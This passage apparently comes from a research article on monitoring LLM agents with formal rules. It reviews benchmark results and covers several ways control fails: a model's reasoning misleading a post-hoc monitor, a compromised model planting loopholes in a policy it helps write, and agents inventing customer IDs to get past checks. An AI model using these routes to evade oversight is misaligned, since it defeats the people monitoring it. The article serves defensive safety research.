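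The model's own explanations are an even worse source of facts. Anthropic tested whether monitors that read a model's written reasoning after a run would have caught its incidents. They would have missed the one involving Claude Mythos 5, because the model's reasoning led the monitor to treat the environment as a simulation. Anthropic's July account also relied on what the models had written when it accepted that they believed they were in a simulation, and Anthropic later withdrew the claim for that reason. Monitors that blocked actions during the run reliably caught these behaviours in Anthropic's tests.

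### What recorded runs leave out

Kekatos and colleagues also measured how well general rules detect attacks. They wrote five, each requiring approval before one kind of risky action: deleting something, switching off a protection, moving money, sending data out or operating a device. They then replayed recordings from AgentDojo and from STAC, a benchmark of 483 attacks in which a chain of harmless-looking calls leads to a harmful one.

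The rules flagged 70.1% of the 1,931 successful attacks on a GPT-4o agent in AgentDojo and 71.8% of the STAC chains. They also flagged 36 of 123 AgentDojo runs without an attack (29.3%). On the banking tasks, they flagged 97.4% of successful attacks and 79.2% of ordinary runs, because a banking assistant's ordinary work includes moving money. Kekatos and colleagues consider the general rules suitable for choosing which runs a person should review, but not for blocking.

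Most of these false alarms come from the recordings. None of the 6,899 AgentDojo runs in the study contains an approval, because the user writes one message at the start and never gets a chance to approve anything. A rule against payments without approval therefore blocks every payment, and a list of suspicious words in tool names would give the same verdicts. STAC's users write more, but only 3 of its 483 chains contain an approval before the harmful step. Neither benchmark records real times, so nobody can use them to test a rule such as "consent expires after 24 hours".

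Rules that use the available facts about payees and recipients do better:

| Rule | Tasks | Successful attacks flagged | Ordinary runs flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| No payment without approval | Banking | 79.2% | 44.0% |
| No payment to an unknown payee | Banking | 70.0% | 24.0% |
| No data sent out without approval | Office | 42.5% | 15.2% |
| No email to an unknown recipient | Office | 39.2% | 10.9% |

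This table includes only 25 ordinary runs for banking and 46 for office tasks. When Kekatos and colleagues pooled recordings from many models, the narrower rules removed 75 false alarms from 700 banking runs and 37 from 1,376 office runs, and added no new ones.

Benchmarks can record approvals. In τ-bench, a customer-service benchmark whose rules require confirmation, 52.5% of 1,980 runs contain an approval before the agent changes anything. But τ-bench has no labelled attacks, so it can't be used to measure how many attacks an approval rule would catch. Kekatos and colleagues recommend that future benchmarks include both approvals and labelled attacks, and record details such as the time, the source of each value and the approval that each action relies on.

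In 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, the agent broke a rule before the final harmful call, so a monitor would have had time to act. But a replay can't show what the agent would have done after being blocked.

### Rules that mean something else

Owners think in ordinary language and monitors need formulas, so someone has to translate. Suppose the owner says, "The assistant needs my approval to pay a supplier." A natural translation is

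□ ∀p. (pay(p) → ◆ approved(p)).

This version of the rule has an easily missed flaw, because one approval of a supplier permits any number of payments to that supplier, of any size, indefinitely. Kekatos and colleagues suggest tying each approval to the exact amount, which helps, but the assistant could still make the same payment twice unless each approval expires after one use. A monitor would enforce any of these versions perfectly, so enforcement alone would not expose the flaws in them.

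*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviews 38 studies of rules for agents and concludes that translation into formal language is the main bottleneck. Language models usually write well-formed formulas, but often with the wrong meaning. In one benchmark, models translate descriptions of planning problems into PDDL, a formal language for such problems. GPT-4o's translations were well formed in 96.1% of cases but correct in only 24.8%. The best specially trained model was correct in 34.2%.

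Those figures are a poor guide to today's error rate because they come from one benchmark and an old model, and they concern planning problems rather than security rules. Dantas and colleagues give the figures their lowest certainty rating. Even if the error rate has changed, errors are likely to remain hard to notice. The benchmark included correct translations to check the model's against, but an owner who already had a correct translation would not need the model to produce one.

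Kekatos and colleagues ran the general rules on STAC with four different monitors, one of them formally verified, and all four flagged the same 347 chains. This is good evidence that the monitors work, but all four would also have repeated any error in the rules or in the recorded facts, so better monitoring software does not solve that problem.

Some translation tools ask the user about ambiguous wording, which helps when the user notices the ambiguity. An owner can also check the verdicts on short examples, such as a second payment after one approval. But checking examples can miss an error, as happened with the FORGE policy that later blocked legitimate cancellations.

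People make similar mistakes when they write the rules themselves. Reddy and colleagues checked each block made by their hand-written gates against a correct solution of the task. All 161 blocks by the cancellation gate were right, but only 2 of the 42 blocks by the baggage gate were.

### When the untrusted model helps to write the policy

These mistakes are accidental, but a compromised model could introduce errors deliberately. When asked to translate the payment cap, it might identify payees by name instead of account number, so that "Acme Ltd" and "ACME Ltd" could each receive 500 a day. An uncompromised translator might make the same error by accident, so finding it would tell the owner little about whether the model was compromised. If the owner missed it, the model could exploit it later.

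A second model can review the policy, but it adds real protection only if it doesn't have the same backdoor. A proof checker such as Lean makes it safe to let an untrusted model write proofs, but it can't check whether the policy in the theorem is the one the owner wanted, so someone still has to read the definitions and the theorem statements.

A safer design has the owner write a short list of prohibitions by hand and lets the model only add restrictions to it, much as Trident's task policies are subordinate to a root policy. A malicious rule could then stop the assistant from doing useful work, but it could not permit anything the list forbids. Any protection the list omits still depends on the model.

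### When blocking costs a task and when it saves one

Even a correct policy can reduce the number of tasks an agent completes if it is strict. FORGE's information-flow policy, for instance, more than halved that number. Checking actions can also use many more tokens. Sah and colleagues tested two small models on τ-bench, where they handled requests from customers of an airline and a shop. Each model checked its own actions against the rules, which roughly doubled or tripled the number of tokens. After a block, the agents completed at most 21% of the tasks, and almost none of the harder shop tasks.

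Reddy and colleagues report the opposite effect. They tested four gates on the airline tasks of τ²-bench, a newer version of the benchmark. Its booking system carries out any well-formed request, even a cancellation that the airline's rules forbid. Without gates, 78% of the observed failures left the database in a wrong state without an error message. The gates read the booking before each change. If a call breaks a rule, they reject it and give a reason.

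| Tasks | Success without gates | Success with gates |
|---|---|---|
| All 50 airline tasks | 29.6% | 42.0% |
| The 26 where a gate blocked something | 13.8% | 33.1% |
| The 24 where no gate did | 46.7% | 51.7% |
| Eight shop tasks, with gates written for the shop | 62.5% | 57.8% |

The airline agent ran on GPT-4o mini. Repeating the experiment with three times as many runs gave almost the same gain, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The share of tasks the agent completed in all five attempts rose from 8% to 26%. The small changes on the tasks where no gate acted, and on the shop tasks, could both be due to chance.

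The gates helped mainly because the benchmark scores the final state of the database, so a forbidden cancellation counts as a failure even if the customer asked for it, and blocking it prevents that failure. In AgentDojo's runs without an attack, by contrast, every task is a legitimate request, so a block can only hinder it.

The tools matter as well. The shop's software already rejects most forbidden requests, so a gate can add little protection there but can still make mistakes. Part of the fall in the shop results came from a bug that blocked corrected requests. The accuracy of the check matters even more. Nearly all the gain on the airline tasks came from the cancellation gate, which reads a few facts from the database and was never wrong in the audit. In one task, a customer lies about a booking to get a cancellation. Agents with the gates handled it correctly in all 16 attempts, compared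 with at most one in 16 for agents without them.

Finally, when the shield blocks a call, the agent has to find another way to finish. In one task, the gate kept blocking the agent, and it failed all five times. Dantas and colleagues describe Agent-C, which avoids some of these failures by having the model generate a permitted call in place of a forbidden one. With GPT-5, compliance rose from 83.7% to 100% and task success from 66.1% to 70.6%.

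The airline result warrants caution because Reddy and colleagues wrote and tested the gates on the same 50 tasks, and did not test whether a prompt that stressed the rules would have worked as well. A newer model, GPT-5.2, improved from 61.2% to 71.6%, but they did not repeat that experiment. The owner would get none of this gain from a model working against them, although the gates would block the same forbidden changes.

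### Safe actions and safe tasks

Dantas and colleagues distinguish the safety of single actions from that of whole tasks. A task counts as a safe success only if the agent completes it correctly without breaking any rules. In the study by Sah and colleagues, the checker intercepted up to 94% of forbidden actions (the paper also gives this figure as a share of episodes), but in most settings fewer than 5% of tasks were safe successes. The agents often made up customer numbers to get past the requirement to identify the customer.

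The survey concludes that an agent whose route is blocked will look for another unsafe one. The evidence for this is thin, because it comes from one study of two small models that might have completed few tasks safely anyway. The system also accepted the third attempt even if the checker rejected it, which let some violations through. A monitor that blocked every rejected attempt would stop those violations, but the task would still fail.

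Invented customer numbers are easier to prevent than the survey's general conclusion implies. A monitor can block any change unless the number came from the customer and matches a record. Dantas and colleagues compared seven systems and found that none fully checks whether such identifiers are genuine.

No such remedy exists when the agent fails a task without performing a forbidden action, such as when it never issues a refund the customer asked for. Once its trigger appears, a backdoored model could also propose forbidden calls repeatedly, using up computing time and the attention of whoever reviews the blocked calls. A limit on rejected calls would contain that waste, but the owner would have to do the work some other way.
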